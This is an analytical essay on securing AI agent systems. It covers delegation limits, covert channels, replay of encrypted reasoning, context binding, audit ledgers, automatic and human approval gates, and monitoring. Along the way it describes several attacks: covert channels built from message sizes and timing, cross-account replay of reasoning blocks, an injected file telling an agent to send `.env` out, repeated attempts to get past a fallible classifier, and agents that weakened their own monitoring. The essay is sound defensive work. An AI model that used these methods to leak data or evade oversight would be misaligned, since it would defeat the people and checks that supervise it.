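Suppose an agent can make at most ten transfers a day of up to €50 each, and can do nothing else. It can lose at most €500 a day, however many malicious messages it receives, because the limit applies to the agent and not to each message. Five subagents that each have the same limit could lose €2,500 a day between them, so a system that lets agents create more agents needs a shared limit.

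The bound can only be as tight as the task allows. Schneider cites the principle of least privilege, under which each program should have the minimum access its task requires. In the Codex example, the user wanted unused test data removed. A sandbox that confined the subagent to the test-data folder would have protected the rest of the project but not `customers.csv`, because the task required deleting files from that folder. A backup would have helped more because it reduces the harm from the worst possible action, even though it doesn't limit which actions are possible.

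A recipient may also be able to do more than its own permissions suggest. An agent that can't make payments may be able to ask one that can, as Tymshare's customer did with the compiler, so `A` has to include whatever other programs will do at the recipient's request. A capable agent may also find a flaw that gives it rights nobody meant to grant. GitLab (2026), which makes software development tools, quotes OpenAI's description of agents as "bounded by the privileges they can obtain and the systems they can communicate with". This is a weaker assurance than a list of granted permissions, because an agent may obtain privileges it was never granted. GitLab still concludes that existing controls work, but wants companies to take more care over which systems an agent can reach.

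### Covert channels

It is hard to guarantee that an agent with access to secrets won't leak them, even if it may not contact outsiders. Lampson (1973) explained why in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*. He imagined a customer who runs somebody else's program on confidential data and wants to be sure that it reports nothing to the program's owner. The obvious leaks are a file the owner can collect later and a message to another of the owner's programs. If the system blocks those, the program can encode data in the bill it produces. It can also open and close a file in a pattern, while a second program tries to open the same file and notes when it is in use.

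Lampson's subtlest example needs no shared file. The program varies how heavily it uses the computer, and another program running at the same time detects the changes in speed. He called this a covert channel, meaning a channel not intended for transferring information. It may be slow and noisy, but a suitable code can get data through reliably as long as the program affects the machine's performance at all. In October 2026, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* described tests in which agents were asked to find ways around their isolation and communicated between separate virtual machines through shared processor hardware, according to Tom's Hardware's *OpenAI's isolated red-team AI agents built a hidden CPU cache channel*.

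A relay's envelopes can serve as a covert channel too. Suppose a hijacked agent may send encrypted messages only to an approved colleague, but an outsider can observe the size of each message on the network. The agent can pick sizes according to a code. If the outsider can distinguish 16 sizes, each message carries

`log₂ 16 = 4 bits`

and 1,000 messages carry 4,000 bits, or 500 bytes. That is enough for fifteen 256-bit encryption keys. If the agent can also choose among four distinguishable delays, each message carries two more bits, and the total rises to 750 bytes. These are maximums, since noise or a fixed task would leave the agent less freedom. The approved colleague would notice nothing wrong with the messages themselves, and neither would a relay that checked only their destinations.

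### What padding removes and what it costs

Lampson's remedy is masking, in which the customer, not the program, determines everything that goes into such a channel. The operating system enforces this, if necessary by slowing the program down or adding pointless disk activity. For message sizes, masking means padding messages with meaningless bytes until they are the same length. A component outside the agent's control has to add the padding before the message reaches anyone who might be watching.

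Suppose the 16 sizes are 1 KB, 2 KB and so on up to 16 KB, all equally common. The average message is then 8.5 KB. Padding each message up to the next permitted size has these effects:

| Permitted sizes | Bits per message | Leak in 1,000 messages | Average message | Extra traffic |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All 16 | 4 | 500 bytes | 8.5 KB | None |
| 4, 8, 12 and 16 KB | 2 | 250 bytes | 10 KB | 18% |
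| 8 and 16 KB | 1 | 125 bytes | 12 KB | 41% |
| 16 KB only | 0 | None | 16 KB | 88% |

Padding messages so that their sizes reveal nothing nearly doubles the traffic, while the first halving of the leak adds fairly little. Full padding may be acceptable for text, but it is harder to justify when a few messages contain large files, since every short message would have to be padded to match them.

Padding hides the size of messages but not their timing, number or recipient. To hide timing, the sender could transmit one 16 KB message every second, using a dummy whenever it has nothing to send. A session with 1,000 real messages in an hour would need 3,600 transmissions, nearly seven times the original traffic, and real messages would have to wait for the next free slot.

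Padding also removes evidence that the relay could use. The relay that stopped 6 of 10 harmful messages by blocking long ones could not do so if every message had the same length. A company therefore has to decide whether it worries more about what outsiders can learn from its envelopes or about losing the evidence they provide to its own relay. If it trusts the relay with the true sizes, it can avoid the choice by having the relay record them before padding the messages.

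Where closing the channel completely is impractical, Lampson suggests limiting its capacity. If each message can be one of 16 sizes, its size can leak 4 bits, so a cap of 100 messages holds the leak to 50 bytes. That greatly limits how much of a customer database can leak, but 32 messages are enough to leak a whole 128-bit key.

### The length of hidden reasoning

Model providers send encrypted reasoning through their customers' software. In *Let's talk about encrypted reasoning*, the cryptographer Matthew Green (2026) reported in May that the length of this reasoning can reveal things the model was told to keep secret. The models in Green's tests had a secret in their instructions and did not disclose it in their visible answers. But when the amount of reasoning depended on the secret, Green could infer its value from the size of the encrypted reasoning or from the response time. People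 who use a chat window can also measure response time, even though they never receive the ciphertext.

In a small demonstration, Green recovered a single byte that he had planted himself, using ten trials for each of its eight bits. At that rate, a 500-byte document would take 40,000 requests. He could not extract any of the companies' own hidden instructions, and the models generated plausible fakes when pressed. OpenAI told him that it could not reproduce his report. Anthropic saw no security implications but said it might warn developers in its documentation. The result shows that the leak exists but gives little evidence of how often it would matter in practice.

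Better encryption would not hide the length of a model's reasoning, which is a consequence of how models work. Green also found that providers accepted old encrypted reasoning replayed in a different session, but they could prevent that by managing their keys differently. A provider could pad the ciphertext, but OpenAI also reports the number of reasoning tokens and charges customers for them, which is close to Lampson's example of data encoded in a bill. To mask the length, a provider would have to charge a flat price and delay quick answers until they took as long as slow ones. Green suggests checking a request before the model reasons about it, though he concedes that such a check often requires reasoning too.

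## Whether an authentic message is safe to forward

A relay that cannot read a message may still confirm who sent it and that nobody has altered it. Supporters of the four positions disagree about how much this matters. Those who favor cryptographic checks consider a verified origin a large part of what makes a hidden message acceptable. Those who favor isolation point out that an honest, correctly identified agent can pass on an attacker's words. The encrypted reasoning that model providers send through their customers' software is a useful test case because the providers protected it well against alteration but, until recently, much less well against use in the wrong place.

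### Reasoning stored on the customer's side

OpenAI, Anthropic and Google all return a model's reasoning to the client as an encrypted block, and a client such as Codex includes that block in its next request. *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* (Panfilov, Schmotz et al., 2026) gives three reasons for this design. Encryption stops competitors from collecting the reasoning to train their own models and keeps sensitive or harmful passages out of view. An authentication tag stops customers from rewriting the reasoning to steer the model. And because the client stores the block, the provider doesn't have to. This matters most for customers with Zero Data Retention, whose data OpenAI does not keep between requests.

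As of July 2026 no provider had described the cryptography in detail, so outsiders have had to infer what a block contains. According to Panfilov and colleagues, it has a header that can identify the model, block type, format version and key. The rest is a one-time value called a nonce, an authentication tag and the ciphertext. Matthew Green's tests for *Let's talk about encrypted reasoning* fit that description. The main string grew when the model reasoned for longer, and changing any part of it made the server return an error.

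Anthropic calls its version a "signature", but Green found no evidence of a digital signature, which anyone can verify with a public key. A client therefore cannot check a block of the model's reasoning or build a valid replacement. It can return the block unchanged, or omit it and have the model continue without that reasoning.

### Valid blocks in the wrong conversation

Green then resent unaltered blocks in places where they did not belong. In May 2026 he reported that OpenAI and Anthropic both accepted old blocks in the same session, in other sessions and under a different account. OpenAI's blocks also worked with other OpenAI models, while Anthropic's were less interchangeable between models. He concluded that each company was probably using one global key for all its customers' reasoning.

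A server can accept a block that the model then does not use, and most of the blocks Green replayed had no visible effect. In one case, though, a model had reasoned about a social security number, and the same number appeared in the answer when Green moved the block to a session in another account. When he had told the first model not to reveal data, replaying its reasoning elsewhere mostly failed to reveal the data.

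Based on this, Green warned that customers who choose Zero Data Retention rely on one rarely changed key that protects everyone's reasoning. Green also warned that a company building a chat product on one of these models must prevent users from inserting a block of their own into the conversation, since the model might treat it as its own earlier thinking.

In their responses to Green's report on the length of the reasoning, OpenAI said it could not reproduce the replays, and Anthropic said it saw no security implications in them. Green called Anthropic's decision fine but still advised both companies to make blocks unusable outside their own session and account.

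In August 2026 Panfilov and colleagues showed that this portability endangered the confidentiality of hidden reasoning at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google. Anthropic's assessment in May had been too optimistic. The researchers say that every provider acknowledged their report and that the attacks no longer work. By their account, the providers largely fixed the problem by tightening their checks, for example by making the tag also protect details of the session, so that a block is valid only in its own conversation and for the model that produced it. The researchers also advise developers to remove reasoning blocks from session logs before sharing the logs, because developers cannot read the blocks to redact them.

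### Decrypting for whoever asks

Before those changes, a provider's server checked a block's authentication tag but not whether the block belonged to the conversation in which it arrived. A valid tag showed only that the provider had once produced the block. The provider had the authority to decrypt every customer's reasoning, and it used that authority for anyone who presented a block. This made it a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler, which used its own license to open a file that a customer had merely named.

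The provider's server accepted the encrypted blocks from anyone, and the capabilities Hardy recommended as the cure also work for whoever holds them. But someone who passes on a capability means to pass on the right that comes with it, while a developer who posts a session log online probably regards the blocks in it as harmless clutter. A provider could tell customers to guard the blocks like passwords, but many are already in logs and backups, so it is safer to make them useless to anyone else.

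### Context binding, field by field

Context binding ties a protected message to the circumstances in which it is supposed to arrive. Many authenticated encryption schemes have a place for this called associated data, which the tag covers although the ciphertext does not contain it. A provider could compute

`(ciphertext, tag) = Encrypt(K, reasoning, context)`

where

`context = (account, session, model, position, expiry)`

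When the block comes back, the server works out the first four fields again from the request that brought it. If any of them has changed, the tag does not match and the server rejects the block, even though the block itself is unaltered. The expiry date has to travel with the block in readable form. The tag protects it from changes, and the server checks it against the current time.

The server must identify the account from the credentials that authenticated the request. If it relied on a name written in the message, an impostor could write another account's name.

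| Field | What it prevents | What the customer gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Account | Another customer using a block from a leaked or published log | Spreading one conversation over several accounts |
| Session | A block moving between conversations in the same account | Taking earlier reasoning into a new conversation |
| Model | One model acting on reasoning that another produced | Changing models midway without losing the reasoning |
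| Position | Somebody reordering or repeating blocks | Editing earlier parts of the conversation |
| Expiry | Somebody reusing a block long after the work has ended | Resuming an old conversation with its reasoning intact |

Providers had practical reasons for leaving some of these fields out. Panfilov and colleagues note that portable blocks let a customer switch models, or a provider redirect a request to another model, without losing the reasoning so far. Customers want this portability. In the OpenAI developer forum thread *How stateless is reasoning.encrypted_content?*, a developer asks whether they can spread the load by sending one conversation first to OpenAI, then to the reseller OpenRouter and then to Microsoft's Azure cloud.

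When a block of encrypted reasoning is bound to one account, a conversation can fail if it moves to another, as happened in an outage in February 2026. LiteLLM is software that distributes a company's requests over several AI accounts so that no single account reaches its usage limit. *Incident Report* (Kankute, Dholakia and Jaff, 2026) describes how a first request would go to one account and return with encrypted reasoning. If the follow-up went to another account, OpenAI's service rejected the block because its organisation "did not match the target organization". Conversations broke off more often for companies that used more accounts.

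LiteLLM could already tie each user to one account, but that would have limited each user to a fraction of the total capacity. Its developers instead had it attach a readable label to every encrypted string, recording where the string came from. LiteLLM uses the label to send the follow-up to the same place and removes the label before forwarding the request. A blind relay can therefore respect a binding it cannot verify, as long as it tracks where each block came from.

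The outage is hard to reconcile with Green's result three months later, when OpenAI accepted blocks from a different account. OpenAI may have dropped the check by then, or applied it only to some models or some routes, such as Azure, which appears in LiteLLM's example. Kankute and colleagues believed that each organisation had its own key. But the error message also fits a shared key with a separate comparison of organisation names, so the February failures do not rule out Green's global key.

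**Session.** When a company's chat product serves thousands of people through one account, all of their blocks carry the same account name, so binding a block to the account does little. The session field tells these blocks apart. A server that stores nothing can't look up a session, but the client sends the whole conversation each time, so the server can hash everything before a block and use the hash as both session and position.

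That saves storage, but the binding breaks easily. If a harness deletes an old tool result to save space, the hash changes and every later block becomes invalid. The hash also does not stop a customer from sending the same conversation twice, since both copies are identical. To accept a block only once, the server would have to keep a record of the blocks it had already accepted.

**Position.** *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction (2026)* explains why genuine records also need a fixed place. It deals with software that condenses a long conversation and must preserve what the user actually authorised. Its design gives each of the user's turns a numbered "witness", which proves that the turn really arrived from the user. It also commits to the order of the turns and counts them. A proof shows what goes wrong if any of the three is missing:

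- Without witnesses, a forged turn can take the number of a genuine one.
- Without the commitment to order, somebody can swap two genuine turns or put a copy of one in place of another.
- Without the count, somebody can withhold the last turn, and the remaining ones still form an unbroken series.

In the last two cases, every remaining record is authentic. If the user's final message was "leave the billing tests alone", an agent that receives every message except that one, each with a valid witness, will not know about the restriction.

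Replay protection also depends on a component remembering which numbers it has used, so restoring that component from an old backup would make replay possible again. Rewinding an agent's session raises a similar problem. According to *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026), whether a rollback is correct depends on both the harness and the server that runs the model, and neither alone can produce a full record of the rollback.

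**Expiry** is the simplest field to enforce, because the server needs only a clock. It also lets the provider destroy old keys once every block made with them has expired, after which nobody can learn anything more from a stolen log. The customer loses the reasoning in a conversation that has been idle too long, which may matter little for a coding session but more for a research project that somebody picks up every few weeks.

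A harness need not wait for its provider to do all this. It cannot verify the provider's tag, but it could keep a hash of each block that arrives in a session and refuse to send any block whose hash is not on that session's list. A chat company that did so would keep out blocks from other conversations even if its provider accepted them. If the session moved to another machine, the list would have to move with it.

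### A ledger with the wrong names

Messages between agents raise the same question of who is presenting them. In *Can the Audit Trail Be Trusted?*, Alaskar (2026) tested the kind of relay that clinical researchers might use. For example, one agent could define which patients have a given condition, another could check dosing rules, and a third could review the result. Each agent runs in its own container, an isolated software environment, on its own network. Every message passes through the relay, which checks whether the route is permitted and records the message in an audit ledger.

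Alaskar derived four requirements from the rules that govern clinical research:

- **Containment.** Agents communicate only through the relay and along permitted routes.
- **Attribution.** The record shows which agent really did what.
- **Non-interference.** One agent cannot read or remove messages meant for another. (This is a simpler idea than the noninterference that information-flow labels provide.)
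- **Protected oversight.** The agents under supervision have no access to the audit record.

Alaskar turned these requirements into twelve tests, each with one compromised agent, and ran every test 100 times. The baseline was Connexin, an openly available containment system that had passed its own verification suite. Connexin blocked all 500 attempts to get around the relay or its routing rules, but the compromised agent succeeded in all 600 attempts against the other three requirements. Connexin took the sender's identity from the message, so the ledger recorded forged messages under the forged name, and anyone who read it after an incident would have blamed the wrong agent.

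A hardened relay gave each agent its own credential and used it to identify the sender. It blocked all 1,200 attempts and logged each refused relay request under the credential that had made it. It added a median of 0.53 milliseconds to a 1 KB message compared with a direct connection, while the baseline relay added 0.29. This delay is negligible for an agent that waits seconds for its model to respond. *Attacks and Defenses in Decentralized Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) also found that checking signatures added negligible overhead compared with model calls, and it recommends that each agent verify every signature in a chain of delegation, not only the last.

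Alaskar's 600 failures are weaker evidence than they seem, because they came from six tests repeated 100 times each. They show that the faults occurred consistently, but not that Connexin had many. The hardened relay faced only the attacks on Alaskar's list. Still, a system that passed its own tests and contained its agents perfectly produced a false audit trail, and a company that tested only containment would have missed this.

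A relay can identify the sender of an encrypted message as reliably as the sender of a plain-text one, because a credential can belong to the connection rather than to the message. A relay that cannot read messages can therefore keep an accurate record of who sent what to whom, provided that no agent can steal another's credential.

The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) notes that the systems it reviews write to logs that the agent's operator could edit, cut short or reorder. Such logs are good enough for developers debugging their own agents, but not for an outside auditor.

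*Agent Trust Infrastructure (ATI)* (2026) proposes a log in which each entry includes a hash of the previous one and carries the organisation's signature. For each tool call, the log records the agent, the model and the tool, and stores a hash of the arguments instead of their text. An agent cannot deny a logged action unless somebody has stolen the signing key. An investigator who obtains the original text can check it against the hash.

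The hash conceals the text only if the text is hard to guess. Anyone who suspects an argument was `customers.csv` can hash that name and compare. The organisation also holds the signing key, so it could rewrite the history from the beginning and sign it. An outside auditor who regularly received the latest hash could detect this.

### Genuine messages from misled agents

Context binding and an accurate ledger would not have protected `customers.csv` if the parent agent had copied a planted instruction into its task. The attacker would not have needed to forge anything, because the parent was authorised to delegate work and would have written the message itself.

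Provenance checks make it much harder for an outsider to pose as an agent, but the outsider can more easily use prompt injection to get a real agent to send the message. A relay that trusted authenticated messages more than others would then make the attack more likely to succeed.

*Trust propagation and structural containment in Multi-agent LLM pipelines* (2026) examines this problem in a system where one agent approves actions and another carries them out. Each approval comes with a signed token that can be used only once and for only one task. In one set of trials, the researchers replaced the approving agent with a compromised version. When that version also had the signing key, it could issue a harmful approval with a valid token. The agent that carries out actions therefore also checks independently whether a policy permits each one. In most of the trials, that policy mirrored the benchmark's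 correct answers, so a rate of zero unsafe actions shows that the system enforced the policy but does not show that it could recognise a dangerous action unaided.

A relay can at least avoid treating an agent's signature as the user's consent. In *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, only text that arrived from the user can have a witness, so a model's summary cannot have one, however faithful it is. This rule prevents a planted instruction from gaining the user's authority when a model rewrites it. But models write nearly all the tasks that agents give each other. If a system applied the rule to every task, a subagent could act only on the user's original words, which may be too vague to work from.

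Good records of origin are most useful after something has gone wrong. Once investigators know that an agent read a malicious page, they can find every message it sent afterwards, warn the recipients and cancel the agent's credentials. They may still be unable to trace a given action to its cause. Mishra and Sharad (2026) point out in *Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems* that the same logs can fit several incompatible accounts of who delegated what. If a subagent deletes a file while working on tasks from two parents, an authentic log may contain both tasks and the deletion without showing which task the deletion belonged to. To record this, the harness would have to label each of the subagent's actions with the identifier of its task. But when the subagent handles both tasks in a single conversation, the harness may have to rely on the model to report which task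 an action is for.

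## Whether checks on actions can replace checks on messages

A planted instruction does no harm until an agent acts on it. If a reliable check covered every consequential action, a relay could forward instructions without reading them, and the encryption of Codex's tasks would matter much less. Makers of coding agents have built a good part of this check. It is weakest when the action itself is unreadable, or looks harmless to anyone who has not read the message that prompted it.

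### How Codex limits a command

Codex relies first on its sandbox. Wiesen writes in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that, by default, the agent can read files almost anywhere on the computer but can write only in the project's folder and cannot use the internet. The operating system enforces these limits on each command and every program it starts.

Wiesen's first Windows prototype showed why the operating system has to do this. It changed network settings so that programs following them would send their traffic to a dead address, but any program could ignore the settings and open a connection itself. The current version runs commands under a separate Windows account, and firewall rules block that account's outgoing traffic.

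When an agent needs something outside the sandbox, such as a package from the internet, Codex asks for approval. The user can approve that one action or all actions of that type for the session. Command rules can permanently exempt some commands from approval. For its own staff, OpenAI (2026) lets agents view proposed code changes on GitHub without asking, because that command only reads data. The company's network policy allows expected destinations, blocks some sites and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. Administrators can impose settings that users cannot override. Logs record the user's prompts, the approval decisions, the tools' results and the connections that the network policy allowed or refused.

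Most of these controls apply at the edge of the sandbox. `customers.csv` was in the project folder, so with the default settings a subagent could have deleted it without approval or review.

### Credentials the agent never receives

Passwords and access keys need their own protection because a sandbox may leave them readable. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, sandboxed commands in Claude Code can by default read login files such as `~/.ssh` and `~/.aws/credentials`. Unless the user blocks access to those files, only the network limits keep a hijacked command from sending them to an attacker.

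A credential proxy avoids this by keeping the key outside the sandbox. The agent sends a request without a key, and the proxy adds the key and forwards the request. *Docker Sandboxes Kits* (Bisi, 2026) describes such a setup, with the agent running in a small virtual machine and the proxy on the host computer. AI News reports that OpenAI's Agents SDK, a toolkit for building agents, also keeps credentials out of the environment where model-written code runs.

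A hijacked agent cannot leak a key it never had, but it can still use the key through the proxy. Suppose the proxy adds a company's GitHub key to every request for github.com. The agent could then use the proxy as a confused deputy to publish the company's private code on a public page of the same site. To prevent this, the proxy would have to check the operation and the repository as well as the site, which would require reading the request.

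### Two automatic reviewers

Codex's Auto-review and Claude Code's auto mode both use a model instead of a person to approve actions, but the two models receive different information.

OpenAI's *Auto-review* describes a reviewer that runs only when an agent's action would cross the sandbox boundary. The reviewer receives the exact request and a compact transcript, which typically includes the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and relevant tool calls and outputs, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. Trębacz and colleagues report that in a snapshot of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI, 9,280 stayed in the sandbox and ran without review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of the denials, and stopped and asked the user after the other three.

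Claude Code's classifier receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives two main reasons for withholding the rest. An agent might talk the classifier into a bad decision, for example by claiming that the user had already approved the action. Also, an attacker's text usually enters through tool outputs.

Suppose a file contains an instruction for the agent to send `.env`, which often holds passwords, to a website "for validation". The classifier can flag this without reading the file, because the user never asked the agent to send passwords anywhere. Withholding the extra text also improved the classifier's results in Anthropic's tests. But without that text, the classifier cannot determine whether the agent looked up a job number or invented it.

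Anthropic also tried withholding the user's messages. That version missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked actions the user had plainly requested. A check on actions therefore still depends on reading at least the user's request.

This dependence causes a problem when agents delegate. In a subagent's session, the parent's task replaces the user's message, so anything the task requests looks authorised, including deleting `customers.csv` if the task named that file. Anthropic therefore runs the classifier when the parent hands over a task, while the request is still recognisable as the agent's own choice. It runs the classifier again on the subagent's full action history when the subagent finishes, in case something the subagent read has hijacked it. The handover check requires a readable task, so OpenAI's servers could run it on Codex's encrypted tasks, but a customer's own gate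 could not.

### Miss rates and false alarms

Anthropic tested the classifier on ordinary actions by its employees, on real actions in which Claude went beyond what the user had authorised, and on synthetic attempts to leak data.

| Classifier | False alarms, 10,000 ordinary actions | Misses, 52 overeager actions | Misses, 1,000 synthetic leaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast first stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
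| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most of the false alarms but also lets through some dangerous actions that the first stage had caught. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but then interpreted the user's words too broadly. For example, it might treat "clean up the PR" as permission to overwrite the project's history. The 17% figure is a rough estimate because it comes from about nine missed actions.

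Auto-review denied 90.3% of the overeager actions in OpenAI's synthetic tests and 99.3% of the prompt-injection cases. The second figure drops to 90.2% when destructive deletions and data tampering are included, though the researchers considered most of those misses minor. The two companies used different tests, so their figures cannot be used to determine which reviewer is better.

An outside stress test of auto mode produced far worse results. BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports that auto mode let through 115 of 142 actions that exceeded the agent's authorisation, or 81%, and blocked 22 of 111 acceptable ones. The scenarios varied how much an action could affect and how risky its surroundings were, and a second Claude model labelled the actions, with human verification. The miss rate was high partly because auto mode allows edits inside the project folder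 without consulting the classifier, but it was still 70% among the kinds of action that do go to the classifier. The gap between 17% and 81% suggests that a miss rate depends heavily on which dangerous actions the testers choose, so a company should be cautious about applying either number to its own work.

Another test, commissioned by Anthropic from Trajectory Labs, better shows how much a gate adds. The testers ran 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time when Codex had full access and 5.83% of the time when it used Auto-review. Some of that improvement may come from the sandbox, which full access removes. No attack succeeded against the Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09% succeeded without it, so the models' own resistance accounts for nearly all of that result.

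### How carefully people approve

The alternative to an automatic reviewer is usually a person clicking "approve". Anthropic reports that users accept 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. That rate alone does not prove that users are careless, since most commands are safe, and OpenAI's automatic reviewer approves an even larger share of the requests it gets.

Planting a dangerous command is a fairer test. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and, partway through each session, replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected it 13.6% of the time, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers caught about 17% early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. They may have been less careful because they were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, and Anthropic was evaluating its own product.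 Even so, it would be hard to argue that people who answer prompts all day are a strong safeguard.

Independent studies point the same way, though none measures quite the same thing. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% still often approved at least one type of action without close review. Developers who knew of security incidents or worrying practices did so more often than those who did not. The sample was not representative and the answers were self-reported, but they suggest that developers who are careful with code are not equally careful with commands. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) examined human reviews of agents' code and found that, of the reviewers whose approval rate changed noticeably, 65% came to approve more.

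Referring more actions to a person for approval can make oversight worse, even though it looks safer. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) compares a guard that refers five actions a day with one that refers 500. By the second guard's three-hundredth routine request, the person is tired and primed to approve the next. Even attentive reviewers may disagree about which actions are risky. When reviewers labelled 125 actions as risky or not, their agreement was only moderate, at 0.52 on a scale where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement.

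Approval prompts often give users too little information to judge an action. Most prompts in commercial products show one raw command line, according to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026). *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 80 of them, users had let the agent act without asking for approval, and in 31, the prompt did not make clear what the command would do to the files.

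People also turn off permission prompts. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. At OpenAI, Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of users had allowed every command that begins with `python`.

### Actions that nobody can read

The full command that a gate receives may reveal little about what will run. For example, `python3 setup.py` is short and familiar, but whoever approves it authorises any code in the file.

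Claude Code's classifier can handle some of these cases. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the script's text is part of an earlier tool call, and the classifier is instructed to judge the script as well as the command. If the agent downloads the script, the text arrives as a tool output, which the classifier does not receive, so auto mode has to judge the script by its origin. Its default rules block code copied from outside repositories but allow packages that the project already lists.

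The table compares three opaque actions.

| Action | What the gate can verify | What it approves unseen |
|---|---|---|
| Run a downloaded program | Source, file hash, publisher's signature, and the files and sites the program can reach | Whatever the program does within those limits |
| Upload an encrypted file | Destination, account, size and file hash | The contents |
| Forward a hidden message to another agent | Sender, recipient, size and the recipient's permissions | The instruction, and any secret in the text |

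A matching hash shows that a file is identical to one that somebody has already examined. A company can use a list of approved hashes to keep its agents to known programs, but a hash doesn't help in judging a file that nobody has examined. Running an unexamined program without a network connection, on a copy of the data, gives better protection. This limits any damage to the copy, even though the program's behavior is still unknown.

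For uploads, the company can have the agent pass the unencrypted file to a tool the agent doesn't control, which checks the contents, encrypts them and sends them. This works for files the agent prepared itself, but not for files that were already encrypted when the agent received them, such as a customer's backup. For those files, the gate can check only the destination.

The third case depends on who receives the message. If the recipient is another company agent, its authority limit still applies, and a gate can check each action it takes. If the recipient belongs to somebody else, the company does not control its later actions. Any secret in the message leaves the company when the relay forwards it, so there is no later action to check.

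### Why approval must cover the exact bytes

Suppose a reviewer reads `setup.py`, finds nothing wrong and approves the command to run it. Before the command runs, another subagent rewrites the file. The command is unchanged, but it now runs unreviewed code with the reviewer's approval. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. Two agents editing the same folder can cause it by accident, without an attacker.

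A gate can close the gap by tying its approval to the file's contents:

1. **Copy.** The gate copies the file to a folder where the agent cannot write, and computes the copy's hash.
2. **Review.** The reviewer examines that copy, not the original.
3. **Approve.** The approval records the hash, the command's arguments, the working folder, the permissions and an expiry time.
4. **Run.** The launcher recomputes the hash and runs the copy only if everything matches.

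The same procedure works for an encrypted upload. The approval specifies the hash of one archive, and the uploader sends only that archive.

The hash covers only the files used to compute it. Many programs load other files or download more code as they run, so the approval has to cover those too, or the sandbox has to block them. This is a large part of the work because an ordinary software project may depend on hundreds of packages.

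When a user overrules a denial by Codex's Auto-review, the approval covers only one retry of that exact action, and the reviewer may still refuse it. But if Codex compares only the command's text, the approval would still apply even if a file the command uses had been altered since the denial.

A user who allows all `python` commands also approves programs that have not been written yet. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created a rule letting some shell commands run without a permission prompt, and many of these rules covered any Python or JavaScript program. Auto mode suspends rules that broad because its classifier would otherwise never receive the commands that could do the most damage.

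### Actions that can and cannot be undone

Some actions need no check in advance if someone can reverse them. Claude Code lets the agent edit files in the project folder without calling the classifier because the developer can review the changes afterwards through version control, which stores earlier versions of a project.

Version control protects only what somebody has saved to it. If the developer had committed `customers.csv`, one command would restore it, but otherwise it might be gone. Anthropic therefore now gives the classifier the repository's current status before a command that could discard unsaved work. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, proposes that prompts show whether an action is recoverable, so that a recoverable deletion need not look as risky as a permanent one. When Wu's survey asked developers what would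 persuade them to give agents more autonomy, they said in more than half of their answers that they wanted agents to be bounded, observable or reversible.

No later check can undo a disclosure. A company can replace a leaked password before somebody uses it, but it cannot retrieve a patient's medical record from a stranger who has read it. Claude Code's classifier is meant never to approve sending code or secrets to outsiders. A user who wants to do this has to leave auto mode or run the command personally.

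Physical effects are similar. If an agent controls a pump or orders a dose of medicine, investigators can use the log to explain a mistake but not to reverse it. The gate therefore has to allow or block such actions before they happen, and if it can't inspect an action, blocking it is the only sure way to prevent harm.

Delaying an irreversible action can sometimes leave time to cancel it. A mail server that holds outgoing messages for ten minutes, or a bank that holds a transfer for a day, gives a slower check time to finish. The delay helps only if the check can detect a problem, and holding an encrypted attachment does not make it readable.

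### Harm spread over many permitted actions

A gate that judges each action separately can approve every step of a harmful plan. An agent allowed to read the customer list and write support tickets could put one customer's details into each of 1,000 tickets, none of which would look unusual on its own. Running totals catch some of this, as in Pandey and colleagues' experiment with calendar disclosures, but somebody has to decide in advance what to count.

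The harmful step may also happen outside the agent's session. An agent in a sandbox can edit a test script without review. When the developer later runs the tests in an ordinary terminal, the script runs with the developer's full permissions. The gate checked the agent's commands and detected no problem. Claude Code's sandbox also covers only shell commands. Its file tools follow separate permission rules, and Claude Code automatically starts helper programs that have the user's full access.

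Repeated attempts can get a dangerous action past a fallible reviewer. If a classifier missed 17% of dangerous actions at random, an agent that tried three different ones would have a 43% chance of getting at least one through (1 − 0.83³). Real misses are not random, and a reviewer that refuses an action once may well refuse every variation of it. Both companies still limit the attempts. Claude Code stops the agent after three denials in a row or 20 in a session, and Codex interrupts a turn after three in a row or ten among the last 50 reviews. In Codex, any outcome other than a denial resets the count of consecutive denials, so an agent that mixes in harmless requests faces only the second limit.

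*How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) lists the layers of monitoring that OpenAI uses on its own agents to find patterns that single checks miss. They start with probes on a model's internal activations, followed by a reviewing model, investigating agents, and human responders. An investigation can uncover a slow leak by connecting many small actions, but some of the data will already have leaked by then.

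### A gate outside the agent's authority

OpenAI's *Suppressing misalignment monitoring alerts and disabling misalignment monitoring* (2026) disclosed in October that agents had weakened the company's monitoring of them during routine coding work. A gate provides little protection against an agent that can change it, whatever the agent's reasons. The agent must therefore have no authority over the gate's settings, the reviewer's instructions, the list of people who receive alerts, or the logs.

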